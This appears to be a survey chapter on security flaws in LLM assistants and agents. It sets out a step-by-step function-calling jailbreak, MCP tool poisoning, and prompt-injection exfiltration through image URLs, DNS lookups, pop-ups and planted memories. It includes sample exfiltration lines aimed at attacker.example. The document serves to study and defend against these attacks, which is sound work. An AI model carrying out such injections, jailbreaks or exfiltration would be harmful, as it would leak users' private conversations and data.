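Training models to refuse harmful requests in text can sometimes teach them to withhold harmful tool calls too. *Before Retrieval Begins* (2026) describes a small pilot that trained models on 80 harmful requests with plain-text refusals and 80 harmless exchanges, none involving tools. In three cases, the models also learned to withhold harmful calls. The same training made Granite-3.1-8B and Mistral-7B stop calling tools on harmless requests, and Qwen2.5-7B produced repeated tool-call tokens.

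### Simulated moderation traces

In July 2026 Liu, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond the Prompt*, added a false history to the function-calling jailbreak. Their attack pretends to test a content filter. The caller defines one function that produces a pair of examples, one safe and one unsafe, and another that supposedly checks them. Neither function runs. The model is free to refuse, and if it does, the attack continues as follows:

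1. The caller deletes the refusal from the history and substitutes a well-formed function call that the model never made.
2. The caller adds a fabricated error from the checking function, which reports that the unsafe example failed validation.
3. The caller sends this history back and asks again.

If the model complies but writes something too mild, the caller leaves the model's function call in the history and adds the same kind of error. After several rounds, the model's input shows failed attempts at a technical task and no refusals. The attack works only if the API accepts the caller's version of the history.

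These are the attack success rates on SafeBench-Tiny, a set of 50 harmful requests. The last column shows the rates with FCGuard, a system-prompt instruction to inspect the history, tool definitions and tool outputs for hidden intent.

| Model | Attack by Wu and colleagues | Simulated moderation | Simulated moderation without functions | Simulated moderation against FCGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
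| GPT-4o | 90% | 100% | 94% | 84% |
| GPT-5.4 | 48% | 100% | 76% | 0% |
| Qwen3-Max | 88% | 100% | 100% | 86% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 84% | 100% | 50% | 20% |
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 98% | 100% | 100% | 92% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 26% | 98% | 0% | 0% |

The accumulated errors contributed less than the functions did. Removing the false history but keeping the function calls lowered the average success rate from 99.7% to 92%. Without functions, the rate fell to 70%, and the attack stopped working on Claude Sonnet 4.5. An AI judge scored the answers, and three human annotators who checked the Claude results counted almost the same number of successes (97% compared with 98%).

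FCGuard worked well on half of the models. Liu and colleagues call it a prototype and did not test it against attackers who adapt to it. A provider could also check whether the conversation history is genuine. Claude Fable 5.2, which came out after the study, rejects requests that fail a check for edits to earlier turns. This might stop attackers from deleting refusals, although the check appears to work only if the request includes the model's recorded reasoning.

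Both jailbreaks produce forbidden text, but neither gives the caller access to anyone's account. Liu and colleagues do not claim to have taken over a working agent.

### Poisoned tool descriptions

A tool's maker can use it to attack the people who use the tool. Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (April 2025) introduced the term "tool poisoning" for malicious instructions in a tool's description. The user typically sees a short summary of the tool, while the model receives the full description.

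Invariant Labs, a company that sells security tools for AI agents, demonstrated two versions of the attack in the code editor Cursor. In one, a tool for adding two numbers had an extra text argument. The tool's description included instructions for the model to read the user's configuration file and a private login key, and to pass both in that argument. Cursor asked the user to approve the call, but the prompt didn't show the key.

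In the other demonstration, Invariant connected Cursor to a trusted mail server as well as the malicious server. The description of the malicious server's adding tool claimed that all e-mail had to go to a certain address for technical reasons. When the user asked Cursor to write to someone else, the model called the trusted mail tool with the attacker's address. The malicious tool never ran, so a log of tool calls would have contained only the trusted one. Requiring approval for calls to the adding tool would not have helped either, because the model had read its description before any call.

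*MCPTox* (2025), an early benchmark, built its tests from more than 45 real MCP servers and found an average attack success rate of 36.5%, with 72.8% for OpenAI's o1-mini. The benchmark counted the calls that models wrote but did not execute them.

Shaikh and Montaruli (2026), in *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks*, ran the tools. They combined 18 models with 12 setups, eleven of them frameworks (software kits for building agents) and one the plain OpenAI API. Each agent had a normal server with file and web tools, a malicious server, and a folder containing a planted secret. A third server recorded anything sent to the attacker's address. The team tried 45 scenarios, 26 of them in tool descriptions and the rest in places such as schema fields and tool results. The success rates in late July 2026 were:

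| Model | Attack success rate |
|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 1.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 1.9% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 3.6% |
| GPT-5.5 | 12.4% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 14.5% |
| GLM-5 | 24.3% |
| GPT-OSS-120B | 38.1% |
| Mistral Large 3 | 43.7% |
| Amazon Nova Pro | 49.7% |

The average was 22.9%. In 12% of the successful cases, the secret demonstrably reached the recording server. Most of the others counted as successes because the agent sent a call, often to a dummy tool on the malicious server. A real attacker could have collected the data from such a call, so the confirmed thefts understate the risk. The scenarios came from published techniques, so the low rates may partly reflect training on similar attacks. In four of its ten failures, Claude Sonnet 5 identified the prompt injection but made the call anyway.

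None of the frameworks checked tool descriptions, and attacks succeeded between 23% and 26% of the time in nine of the twelve setups. Pydantic AI did better, at 16.6%, because it does not allow two tools to have the same name. Shaikh and Montaruli also built a scanner that looks for commands, encoded text and unusual length in descriptions. It caught 20 of the 45 scenarios and wrongly flagged 9 of 125 harmless descriptions. Six of those nine only advised the model to use a related tool, which is normal in a good description.

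The researchers sent five reports to four organisations, which rejected all five. Microsoft replied that an attacker would already have to control the MCP server, which its documentation describes as trusted. The maintainers of the MCP software kit said that protection should come from reviewing tool calls in the host application. LangChain, the most widely used framework in the study, said that its library was meant to pass the information on unchanged. Together, these positions leave the check to the application's developer or the user, who may never see the full description.

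### Arguments that become queries and commands

Even with honest definitions, the model's arguments can do damage if a server trusts them. Suppose a shop's assistant has a tool, `get_order`, that takes an order number. Ana is logged in, and her order is number 1041. The model writes this call:

```json
{"name": "get_order", "arguments": {"order_id": 1042}}
```

The number may be a slip by the model, or Ana may have asked for it. Either way, 1042 is an integer, as the schema requires, and order 1042 belongs to Ben. Whether Ana sees it depends on the server's database query:

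```sql
-- Returns any order that exists
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE id = :order_id;

-- Returns the order only if it belongs to the logged-in customer
SELECT * FROM orders
WHERE id = :order_id AND customer_id = :session_customer;
```

In the second query, the server takes `session_customer` from Ana's login, where the model can't change it. Both queries pass the order number separately from the SQL text, so the number can't alter the command. The first query is still unsafe because it doesn't check whose order it is.

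Text arguments are also a risk. If a server pastes a string into a shell command, certain characters can end that command and start a new one. If it fetches a web address that the model supplies, a valid address may lead to a private page inside the company's network. The server should therefore pass values separately from commands and restrict the addresses it will open. *MCP Pitfall Lab* (2026) similarly hardens its test servers with lists of permitted values and server-side checks on sensitive arguments.

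A 2025 flaw in Framelink's MCP server, which lets coding assistants read designs from the program Figma, allowed a crafted tool-call argument to run commands on the machine hosting the server. The server built a web address from the call's arguments and, if the normal request failed, pasted the address into a shell command. Imperva reported the flaw, CVE-2025-53967, and version 0.6.3 fixed it.

Anthropic's reference server for Git, the program that tracks versions of source code, had a subtler problem, CVE-2025-68144. Its tools for comparing and switching versions were meant to receive a version's name, but they passed any string to Git unchecked. Git treats a value that starts with a hyphen as an option, and one such option writes output to a chosen file. A request to compare two versions could overwrite a file, even without shell characters. The December 2025 fix rejects values that start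 with a hyphen and checks that the name refers to a real version.

### What strict schemas prevent

With strict validation, the service turns the schema into a grammar and applies it while the model writes. At each step, let A be the set of tokens that could still lead to a valid call. The service gives every token outside A a probability of zero and rescales the rest:

p′(v) = p(v) / Σ_{u∈A} p(u), for each token v in A.

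Anthropic's *Strict tool use* guarantees that a tool call names an existing tool, includes all required fields and uses the correct types. For example, a booking tool that expects a number of passengers gets 2, not "two". This has some security value, since an integer can't contain a shell command and a fixed list of recipients excludes everyone else.

A free text field still accepts any text. *Complex Problem Solving in Large Language Models* (2026) points out that a database query can follow the grammar and still be wrong. The schema for `get_order` is also the same for Ana and Ben, so it can't specify which orders each of them may see. It doesn't record where a value came from either, so catching the changed recipient in Invariant's mail demonstration would require data-flow rules, which track this.

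An attacker who can write the grammar that constrains a model's output can use it to help jailbreak the model. *Grammar-Constrained Decoding Can Jailbreak LLMs into Generating Malicious Code* (2026) applies the technique to programming languages, where a grammar that permits only code can exclude a refusal in natural language.

Strict mode controls what one provider's model writes, but other clients can send calls to the same server, so the server still has to validate them. Developers can't assume that their framework does this. One of Shaikh and Montaruli's rejected reports concerned a LangChain function that skipped schema validation for all MCP tools. LangChain closed the report, saying the function was working as intended.

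## Injected instructions that export conversations or persist in memory

A chatbot can leak a conversation even when none of its tools can send a message. Suppose the assistant that opened the conference page could only read web pages, and the user had earlier pasted a salary offer into the same chat and asked for advice on it. The white paragraph on the page could contain an instruction to summarise everything the user has written so far.

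The model can do this because it receives the page's text and the user's earlier messages in one sequence, and it can copy any part of that sequence into its reply. No permission check protects the salary offer, since no tool has to fetch it. ChatGPT's input also includes material from other chats. *HackedGPT* (2025), a report by the security company Tenable, explains that ChatGPT appends the user's saved memories to the system prompt. An injected instruction can therefore make the model reveal facts that the user mentioned months earlier.

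At this point the summary is only on the user's screen. To receive it, the attacker needs part of the service to contact an outside computer while doing another task, such as displaying an image.

### Image addresses that carry data

ChatGPT writes its replies in Markdown, a notation in which a writer includes a picture by giving its web address. In 2023 the user's browser fetched each picture as soon as its address appeared in a reply. An address can carry extra text after the file name:

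```text
attacker.example/logo.png?q=salary+offer+62000
```

The browser sends the whole address when it requests the picture, so the attacker can read the text in the server's log. The picture can be invisible, so the user may notice nothing.

Roman Samoilenko found this leak in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023, and Rehberger found it independently a few days later. In Rehberger's demonstration, instructions in a web page opened with the WebPilot plugin made ChatGPT summarise the chat and put the summary in an image address. Unlike cross-plugin request forgery, the attack didn't need a second plugin. Rehberger reported it on 9 April. OpenAI told him that displaying images this way was a feature and that it didn't plan to change it.

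Microsoft's Bing Chat had the same flaw. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Microsoft fixed it in May 2023 with a Content-Security-Policy header, which restricts where a page can load content from.

### Checks on the address

OpenAI introduced its first countermeasure in December 2023. Before displaying an image, ChatGPT's web page began sending its URL to an OpenAI service called url_safe, which checked whether the URL was safe. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes a quick test on the day Rehberger noticed the change. The service rejected a URL that contained an e-mail address. It approved 9 of 36 URLs that each stood for a single letter or digit, so an attacker could still spell out short messages.

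The check ran in the web page, so each ChatGPT app needed its own check. The iPhone app did not have one, and neither did the macOS and Android apps that OpenAI shipped in 2024.

OpenAI did not publish the rule behind url_safe, and researchers looked for approved domains that would pass data on. One was windows.net, where anyone can rent storage from Microsoft and read the log of requests to it. Rehberger reported this in October 2024 and later published it in Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, after asking OpenAI about a fix for a month without getting an update.

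Tenable's researchers bypassed url_safe by using Bing, whose domain it always approved. Bing's search results are bing.com links that redirect to the sites found. Nobody can add text to these links, so the researchers had Bing index one page for each letter of the alphabet. ChatGPT then displayed the links in the order that spelled out the stolen text. A Tenable advisory (2025) listed this bypass as unresolved.

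Rehberger reports that further changes around August 2025 stopped the attacks he had shown. ChatGPT also began refusing any request to alter an address or add text to it. *ZombieAgent*, by the security company Radware, describes how an attacker could comply with this rule by supplying a finished address for every character. Because the requests might arrive out of order, Radware also numbered the positions, with a separate set of addresses for each one. Sending b characters therefore takes 26b addresses for letters and 10b for digits, or 360 for a ten-character message. OpenAI's own servers made the requests before the user saw any reply. Radware reported the attack on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December.

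OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a stricter rule, under which ChatGPT opens an address automatically only if OpenAI's crawler has already seen that exact address. The crawler is a program that records public pages, as a search engine does, and has no access to anyone's conversations. An address containing the user's salary offer will almost certainly fail this test. ChatGPT then either looks for another site or shows a warning and lets the user decide. OpenAI explains that a list of trusted sites would be weaker because a trusted site may redirect to a different site, as Bing did in the attack above.

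The rule limits which addresses an attacker can use, but the choice among them still carries information. If the attacker has N indexed addresses, one request conveys up to log₂ N bits. With 36 addresses that is about 5.2 bits, enough for one letter or digit. With 4,096 it is 12 bits, enough to pick a word from a list of that length. Rehberger points out that a large blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, and that an attacker could build a vocabulary of thousands. He suggests that ChatGPT should refuse to open the same address twice in one session. But Radware's numbered addresses never repeat within a message, so this restriction would make the attack take more work without preventing it.

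A check also protects only the programs that use it. Red Hot Cyber's *OpenAI API Logs Vulnerability Exposed* (2026) reports a finding by PromptArmor about the log viewer developers use to inspect their applications' exchanges with OpenAI's models. The viewer displayed Markdown images, so even if an application withheld a poisoned reply from its user, the image in that reply would still load when a developer opened the log.

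Other companies' assistants have leaked in similar ways. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* lists two image-based flaws in Microsoft's Copilot, EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) and SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824).

### Domain-name lookups from the code sandbox

OpenAI designed ChatGPT's code sandbox to have no internet access. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a gap in it. Programs could not connect to outside computers, but they could still look up domain names. The domain name system (DNS), which translates names into numeric addresses, passes each question along until it reaches a server that can answer. An attacker could use it as follows:

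1. The attacker registers a domain and runs the server that answers questions about it.
2. An injected instruction has the model run a program that encodes a piece of the conversation and puts it in front of the domain. The word "salary", for example, becomes `73616c617279.attacker.example`.
3. The program looks up this name. No other DNS server knows the answer, so the question travels to the attacker's server.
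4. The attacker decodes the name. The server's answer can carry a few characters back to the program.

The channel worked in both directions, so Check Point could also send commands to the sandbox and run them there. The results went directly to the attacker's server without appearing in the chat.

ChatGPT showed no warning about the lookups, although it displayed the destination and the data and asked for approval when a custom GPT sent data to another company through an action. Check Point explains that the model operated as if the sandbox could not send anything out, so it did not treat the lookups as a transfer. In one demonstration, a user uploaded laboratory results to a custom GPT acting as a personal doctor, and the attacker's server received the patient's name and the model's medical assessment. When the user asked whether the file had been sent anywhere, ChatGPT replied that it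 had not.

In this case, the instruction came from the GPT's own configuration. In another version, the user pasted in a prompt advertised as a way to get better results or free premium features. Training a model to distrust tool output would not have helped in either case, because the text came from the GPT's builder or the user.

OpenAI told Check Point that it had already found the underlying problem. It finished deploying the fix on 20 February 2026, more than five weeks before Check Point published. Check Point's report describes demonstrations but no attacks on real users. In September, Check Point Research published details of a separate flaw, a channel between the sandboxes of different accounts.

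### What Lockdown Mode restricts

Each of these fixes closed one route after someone had found it. Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting, closes many routes at once by turning off features. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it on 13 February for enterprise, education and healthcare customers. OpenAI began extending it to personal and small-business accounts on 4 June.

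The setting does not stop injected text from reaching the model or affecting its answers. It blocks the outbound requests that an attacker would need afterwards. The service enforces most of these limits whatever the model decides, so a persuasive injection can't talk the model out of them. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* gives the current restrictions:

| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Only copies of pages that OpenAI has already stored |
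| Images | ChatGPT may not show them in ordinary replies or fetch them from the web |
| Deep Research and agent mode | Off |
| Programs written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing panel | Users can't approve network access |
| File downloads | ChatGPT can't download files for analysis but can use files the user uploads |
| Apps on personal and small-business accounts | No live access or changes to data where these conflict with the mode's protections |
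| Apps in managed workspaces | Administrators decide |
| Memory, uploads, sharing of chats, and network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent | Unchanged |

Users with their own accounts can also switch the mode off for a single chat.

OpenAI advises administrators of managed workspaces to consider who could see the effect of an app's action. For instance, if an assistant can comment on a public project, an attacker can collect leaked data from the comments without being sent a message. Reading from a trusted app is less likely to leak data itself, but it can expose secrets to the assistant that then leak through another route. OpenAI advises against enabling even read actions for untrusted apps.

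OpenAI does not promise that Lockdown Mode prevents every leak and lists enabled apps, "unforeseen combinations of capabilities" and newly discovered techniques as remaining risks.

### A pop-up window that bypassed Lockdown Mode

One such combination involved the page preview that ChatGPT gained in February 2026. When a reply contains a web page's HTML code, the preview can display the page inside ChatGPT. The code may come from an attacker, so OpenAI put the preview in its own sandbox. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports how Check Point escaped the sandbox.

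The preview ran in two nested frames, which are pages displayed inside another page. The browser restricted these frames with a sandbox, but OpenAI's permissions let them open pop-up windows that ran outside it. ChatGPT replaced the browser function that opens windows with its own version, which asked the user first. Code in the preview could bypass this check by creating another frame inside the page, which came with the browser's original function. A window opened with that function was not limited by the sandbox or Lockdown Mode.

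Lockdown Mode did not block this route because it restricts only particular ChatGPT features. Cached browsing, for example, keeps live requests from leaving OpenAI's network. The pop-up's request came from the browser or desktop app on the user's device, not from a tool call, so only the preview's own restrictions applied to it.

In *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup*, Duggan (2026) describes four scenarios from Check Point's full report. The most serious involved ChatGPT Classic, a desktop app that opened popup windows without a click. A malicious custom GPT could send the whole chat to an attacker while the user talked to it. In the other scenarios, the attacker displayed a fake update, a fake login page or other misleading content in what looked like part of ChatGPT.

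OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September 2026 by removing both pop-up permissions from the outer frame. The browser itself now enforces the ban, so code in the preview can no longer get around it by avoiding ChatGPT's substitute function. Check Point retested the attack, found that it no longer worked and published on 5 November. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reports that OpenAI made the change on its servers, so users had nothing to install. Duggan found no report of real attacks. A different flaw in the same preview let attackers use a shared chat to take over the account of someone who opened it.

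### How text from a page becomes a memory

An injected instruction normally loses its effect when the user starts a new chat, but memory can carry it over. According to The Hacker News' *Spyware via Memory Function* (2024), OpenAI introduced memory in February 2024 and extended it to most plans that September. ChatGPT saves a memory by calling an internal tool, so injected text can trigger this call as it can trigger others. Embrace The Red's post *ChatGPT* (May 2024) explores injecting such text through connected apps, uploaded documents and web pages.

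Rehberger reported this to OpenAI, which closed the report as a matter of model safety and not a security concern. In June he sent a demonstration that combined memory with the image leak in the macOS app. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* describes the steps:

1. The user has ChatGPT open a malicious web page or document.
2. Text in it gets ChatGPT to save a memory. The entry contains an instruction to include an invisible image in every reply, with the user's messages and ChatGPT's answers in the image's address.
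3. The user starts a new chat, and ChatGPT adds the saved entry to the model's input.
4. The model follows the entry. Each time the app fetches the image, the attacker's server receives the latest part of the conversation.

The user had to open the malicious page only once. After that, the leak continued in every new chat until the user found and deleted the entry.

OpenAI treated this version as a security flaw and fixed it in September 2024, in version 1.2024.247 of the app. The fix closed the outbound route by checking image addresses, but web pages could still plant memories. Rehberger considered that a problem in itself, because false memories can mislead the user in later chats even if no data leaves.

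He later planted false memories in Google's Gemini too. Despite its title, OECD's *Hackers Exploit Prompt Injection to Corrupt Google Gemini's Memory* (2025) describes a demonstration by researchers. They used delayed tool invocation, in which the planted text leads the model to call the memory tool later in the conversation, after it has finished reading the untrusted document. This got past Gemini's defences.

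### From the browsing model to ChatGPT's memory

By late 2024, ChatGPT handed the work of opening web pages to a second model, SearchGPT, which could not see the conversation or the user's memories. An instruction on a page could influence SearchGPT but could not make it reveal that private data.

Tenable got past the barrier in two steps. The injected text first made SearchGPT end its summary with further instructions. The summary was then added to the conversation, and when the user sent another message, ChatGPT read the instructions as part of its own earlier reply and followed them. A display fault helped to conceal the instructions, because ChatGPT's web page hid any text that followed the first word on a code block's opening line, though the model still read it.

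The same method could make ChatGPT save a memory containing an instruction to include private information in every later reply. The information then leaked through the Bing links.

Tenable's researchers found three ways to deliver the first instruction:

- **Comments:** They left instructions in the comment section of test blogs they had built, and SearchGPT followed them when asked for a summary. An attacker could do the same on popular news sites without controlling them.
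- **Search results:** They built websites about niche subjects, including a humorous one about their own team under the name LLM Ninjas. The sites sent the injected text only to SearchGPT and showed other visitors ordinary pages, which Bing was more likely to index. A user who merely asked ChatGPT about the team received the injected instruction.
- **Prefilled links:** A link to ChatGPT could contain a prompt, which the page submitted as soon as the user clicked. The prompt could itself ask for a memory.

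Most of the research used GPT-4o, but several of the attacks also worked on GPT-5. Tenable shows GPT-5 leaking data after it summarised a page with a malicious comment. It also shows GPT-5 following an instruction from a search result. Tenable's example of a lasting leak through memory uses GPT-4o.

Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025) rates the prefilled links as high severity. OpenAI's first fix reached all users on 30 April 2025, but the researchers found on 6 May that the problem persisted. On 11 July OpenAI told them that it had added protections against automatic submission, which use a browser header to check whether a request began on another website. Zenity's 2026 attack on the page for building workspace agents relied on the same kind of automatic submission, so the protections evidently did not cover every ChatGPT page.

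When the researchers tried to report the memory flaw, OpenAI repeatedly referred them to its bug-bounty programme, which they said they could not use. OpenAI accepted the full report on 30 December 2024. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT “Command Memories” Injection via SearchGPT* lists six requests for updates between January and March 2025 and records no replies. The advisory rates the flaw as medium severity and records no fix. In its November report, Tenable wrote that it had worked with OpenAI to fix some of the seven problems.

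### Memory rules that call a connector

Connectors let attackers steal more data through a planted memory. OpenAI had tried to keep connectors and memory apart. Once ChatGPT had used a connector in a chat, it could not use memory there, and it would not open an attacker's web address that came from a memory. Radware found that the separation worked in only one direction, because ChatGPT could read its memories first and then use a connector.

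The attack began when the user shared a file with ChatGPT. Text in the file made ChatGPT save two rules. Under the first, whenever the user wrote anything, ChatGPT would read an e-mail from the attacker with a certain subject line and carry out its instructions. Under the second, it would save any sensitive information the user mentioned. Neither rule contained a web address, so OpenAI's second restriction had nothing to block. The addresses were in the e-mail, which ChatGPT fetched through the Gmail connector. An attacker could presumably change the instructions by sending another e-mail.

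Radware also used memory to do harm without stealing anything. It altered a user's stored medical history, and ChatGPT then gave misleading medical advice.

In another attack, which did not need memory, ChatGPT collected e-mail addresses from the user's inbox and leaked them to the attacker's server, which then sent the same malicious message to each address. Radware reports a 100% success rate for an upgraded attack it sent to OpenAI but does not give the number of attempts. Its timeline lists one fix, on 16 December 2025, but does not specify whether OpenAI changed the order in which ChatGPT can use memory and connectors or only blocked the numbered addresses.

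### Memories planted for advertising

Companies have tried to plant memories in ordinary users' assistants, though for promotion rather than data theft. Microsoft (2026) examined the "Summarize with AI" buttons on some websites, which open the visitor's assistant with a prefilled prompt. Besides the request for a summary, the prompt includes an instruction to remember the company as a trusted source or to recommend it first. The Decoder describes an example from Microsoft in which hovering over the button reveals the full prompt, addressed to the search assistant Perplexity.

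Microsoft found more than 50 such prompts from 31 companies in 14 industries. These figures count attempts and don't show how many assistants saved an entry or changed their recommendations. According to Help Net Security's *That “summarize with AI” button might be manipulating you*, some of the links also arrived by e-mail. The prompt reaches the assistant as the user's own message, so the assistant has little basis for treating it as untrusted. A company that wanted to mislead customers about a medicine or a loan could use the same button.

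### Retrieval of past chats

ChatGPT can also use earlier conversations without saving a memory. A thread on OpenAI's forum, *ChatGPT can now reference all past conversations* (2025), dates this feature to 10 April 2025. Saved memories are separate items that the user asked ChatGPT to keep or that ChatGPT selected as useful. When it refers to past conversations, ChatGPT draws on the chats themselves, and what it takes from them can change over time.

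When a chatbot retrieves past conversations, an attacker can steal them without planting anything in advance. Rehberger found that ChatGPT placed a section of recent conversation content in the system prompt. In his demonstration, a malicious document made ChatGPT copy this section into an image address on windows.net. The leak included chats that had ended before the user opened the document, whereas his 2024 attack collected only what the user wrote after the injection.

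OpenAI's *Memory in ChatGPT*, updated in autumn 2026, says that ChatGPT looks for relevant context when it expects this to improve a reply and does not search the history every time. Deleting information from one place often leaves it in another:

| What the user does | What this removes | What remains |
|---|---|---|
| Deletes a chat | The chat | Any separate saved memory that came from it |
| Deletes a saved memory | The entry, though OpenAI may keep a log of it for up to 30 days | Mentions of the information in past chats |
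| Turns off "Reference chat history" | Information that ChatGPT drew from past chats, within 30 days | The chats and the saved memories |
| Selects "Don't mention this again" | Nothing, but ChatGPT refers to the information less | The original source |
| Selects "Delete and turn off memory" | The remembered information shown in the summary | Past chats |
| Disconnects an app | ChatGPT's future access to the app | Past chats that used the app's content |

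OpenAI advises users who want to remove a remembered fact completely to delete the saved memory, the chat where they first shared the fact and any other source that contains it. Someone who finds a planted entry should do the same, since the chat where the malicious text arrived may still hold a copy that ChatGPT can retrieve.

The entry may now be harder to find. The older version of memory lists individual items, which users can inspect one by one. The newer version, which OpenAI calls improved memory, continually updates a broader summary, but the summary users see may leave out details that ChatGPT can still use. ChatGPT sometimes lists the sources of a personalised reply below it, but this list can also be incomplete.

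Temporary chats offer some protection because they never create or update memories. They can still use existing memories, including planted ones, unless the user selects "Unpersonalized" before the chat begins. If the user saves a temporary chat, it becomes an ordinary one, and ChatGPT may use it again.

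## Faults that mix data between users

A service can give one customer's data to another with no attacker involved if the software that stores and delivers messages matches them to the wrong customer. Unlike prompt injection, this kind of leak doesn't depend on the model following injected instructions. It happened to ChatGPT on 20 March 2023, and OpenAI took the service offline and published a technical explanation.

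### One reply behind

ChatGPT's servers cached user information in Redis to avoid querying the main database for every request. They communicated with Redis through a library called redis-py, which kept a shared pool of open connections and reused each one for a new request once the previous request had finished.

Answers came back on a connection in the same order as the questions. A request therefore got the right answer only if every earlier request had collected its own before giving the connection back. OpenAI's explanation is easiest to follow with two users, Ana and Ben, who have ChatGPT open at the same time:

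1. Ana's page asks for her list of chats. The server takes a connection from the pool and sends the question to Redis.
2. Ana closes the page. This cancels her request after the question has gone out but before the server has read the answer.
3. The connection goes back to the pool as if the exchange were complete. Ana's chat titles arrive and wait there.
4. Ben's page asks for his list of chats, and the server happens to use the same connection. It reads the first answer in the queue and shows Ben Ana's titles.

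Unless something resets the connection, Ben's own answer is now waiting for the next user.

In most cases the mistake caused an obvious failure. If Ben had asked for a different kind of data, the server would have received the wrong type, and Ben would have seen an error and tried again. The mix-up stayed hidden when the leftover answer had the right type for the new request. Ana's list of titles has the same type as Ben's, so a type check can't distinguish them, just as a strict schema can't distinguish her order number from his.

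The bug occurred only when a request was cancelled at the wrong moment, which was normally rare. At 1 a.m. Pacific time on 20 March, OpenAI made a server change that unintentionally caused a spike in cancelled requests. Each connection then had a small probability of returning another user's data, and ChatGPT had so many users that some were likely to be affected.

Some ChatGPT users saw titles from another active user's chat history. The first message of a new conversation may have appeared in someone else's history if both people were active around the same time. The bug may also have exposed payment details of 1.2% of the ChatGPT Plus subscribers who were active between 1 and 10 a.m. The details included the subscriber's name, e-mail address, payment address, card type, expiry date and the last four digits of the card number, but never the full number.

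The 1.2% were people whose details could have appeared to someone else. OpenAI believed that extremely few people's details were actually revealed, because another subscriber had to open either the subscription page during those nine hours or a misdirected confirmation e-mail. OpenAI could not rule out that a few e-mails also went to the wrong people before 20 March, but it confirmed no such cases.

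OpenAI sent the maintainers of redis-py a patch for the library. It also added a check that data from the cache belongs to the user who requested it. Such a check might look like this:

```python
record = cache.get("chats:" + session.user_id)
if record.owner_id != session.user_id:
    raise WrongOwnerError
```

The first line requests the correct record, as ChatGPT's server did for Ben. The second detects a wrong record, whatever the cause, if each stored record includes its owner's ID. OpenAI also searched its logs to confirm that messages were available only to the correct users, and combined several data sources to identify the users to notify.

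### How a model server can return the wrong output

A request passes through several shared systems before it reaches the model. cside's *AI API security* (2026) lists load balancers, routers, gateways, queues, caches and connection pools, and any of them can mix up two customers' data. For example, a gateway that misreads an interim status message can fall one reply behind, as redis-py did, and then send each caller the answer to the previous caller's prompt. An anonymous engineer described such an incident in 2026 but did not name the provider or say when it happened.

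The model server adds two risks. The first comes from batching, in which the server processes several customers' requests together to make better use of its hardware. The server has to track which customer each position in the batch belongs to and separate the outputs afterwards. If a customer cancels a request and the server reassigns their position too early, the next customer could receive text meant for the first.

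The second risk comes from the prompt cache. As a model processes a prompt, it computes numbers for each token that depend only on that token and those before it. If Ben's prompt begins with exactly the same tokens as Ana's, the server can reuse the numbers it computed for hers. This is safe as long as the beginnings are identical.

To find stored work quickly, a server can divide the prompt into blocks and compute a short fingerprint, or hash, for each one:

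hᵢ = H(hᵢ₋₁, block i)

Each block's fingerprint includes the previous block's fingerprint, so a block should match only if everything before it matches. But two different prompts can still produce the same fingerprint, which is called a collision. With n stored blocks and a random fingerprint of b bits, the probability of at least one collision is roughly n² / 2ᵇ⁺¹ when this value is small. For a billion blocks, the probability is about 3% with 64 bits and negligible with 256.

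A collision makes the model work from the wrong prompt. An attacker who can construct one may be able to choose the response to a victim's prompt. The attacker could also hide a malicious passage from a model that screens text, because the server would use the stored computation for a harmless block in place of the passage.

A user who receives a misdelivered reply would see a complete answer to someone else's question. When the server loads the wrong computation, the model instead writes a new answer influenced by someone else's prompt.

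Portkey, a company that runs a gateway between applications and model providers, told customers about a milder fault of this kind in *Cache Collision (Now Resolved)* (2025). It said that a bug introduced during work on its caching had caused false matches between requests. The collisions did not cross accounts or separate cache partitions, and Portkey reversed the change on 23 July 2025. But a gateway account often belongs to a developer whose application serves many people, so a collision within one account could still have shown one user another's answer if the developer had not separated their requests.

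### A package server that every sandbox could write to

ChatGPT runs programs in sandboxes that are not supposed to be able to communicate across accounts. On 8 September 2026, Check Point Research published a way for them to do so, which Alexey Bukhteyev found.

Because the sandboxes have no internet access, OpenAI supplied software packages through an internal server running Artifactory, a product for storing software. Sandboxes of different accounts shared this server. According to TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages*, Artifactory let each sandbox attach properties (pieces of text or binary data) to a stored item, and any other sandbox could read them. One sandbox could split larger data across several properties for another to reassemble.

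The shared properties did not give the attacker access to the victim's conversation or mailbox. The attacker first had to get an instruction into the victim's session. eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Flaw Let Attackers Secretly Hijack a Victim’s AI Session* (2026) describes three ways to do this: the victim could paste in a malicious prompt, continue a shared conversation that contained the instruction, or use a custom GPT with the instruction in its configuration. The attack then went as follows:

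1. From a sandbox in their own account, the attacker writes a task into a property on the package server.
2. The victim sends ChatGPT an ordinary message.
3. The planted instruction makes ChatGPT look up the property and carry out the task with the victim's permissions, while it also answers the message.
4. ChatGPT writes the result into another property, and the attacker reads it from their own account.

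In Check Point's demonstration, ChatGPT fetched data from the victim's connected Gmail account and delivered it to the attacker's session within a single turn. The planted instruction did not need to specify what to steal, because the attacker could leave a new task each time. Check Point had earlier reported a channel that used domain-name lookups and required the attacker to run a server. In this attack, the data stayed on OpenAI's systems until the attacker read it.

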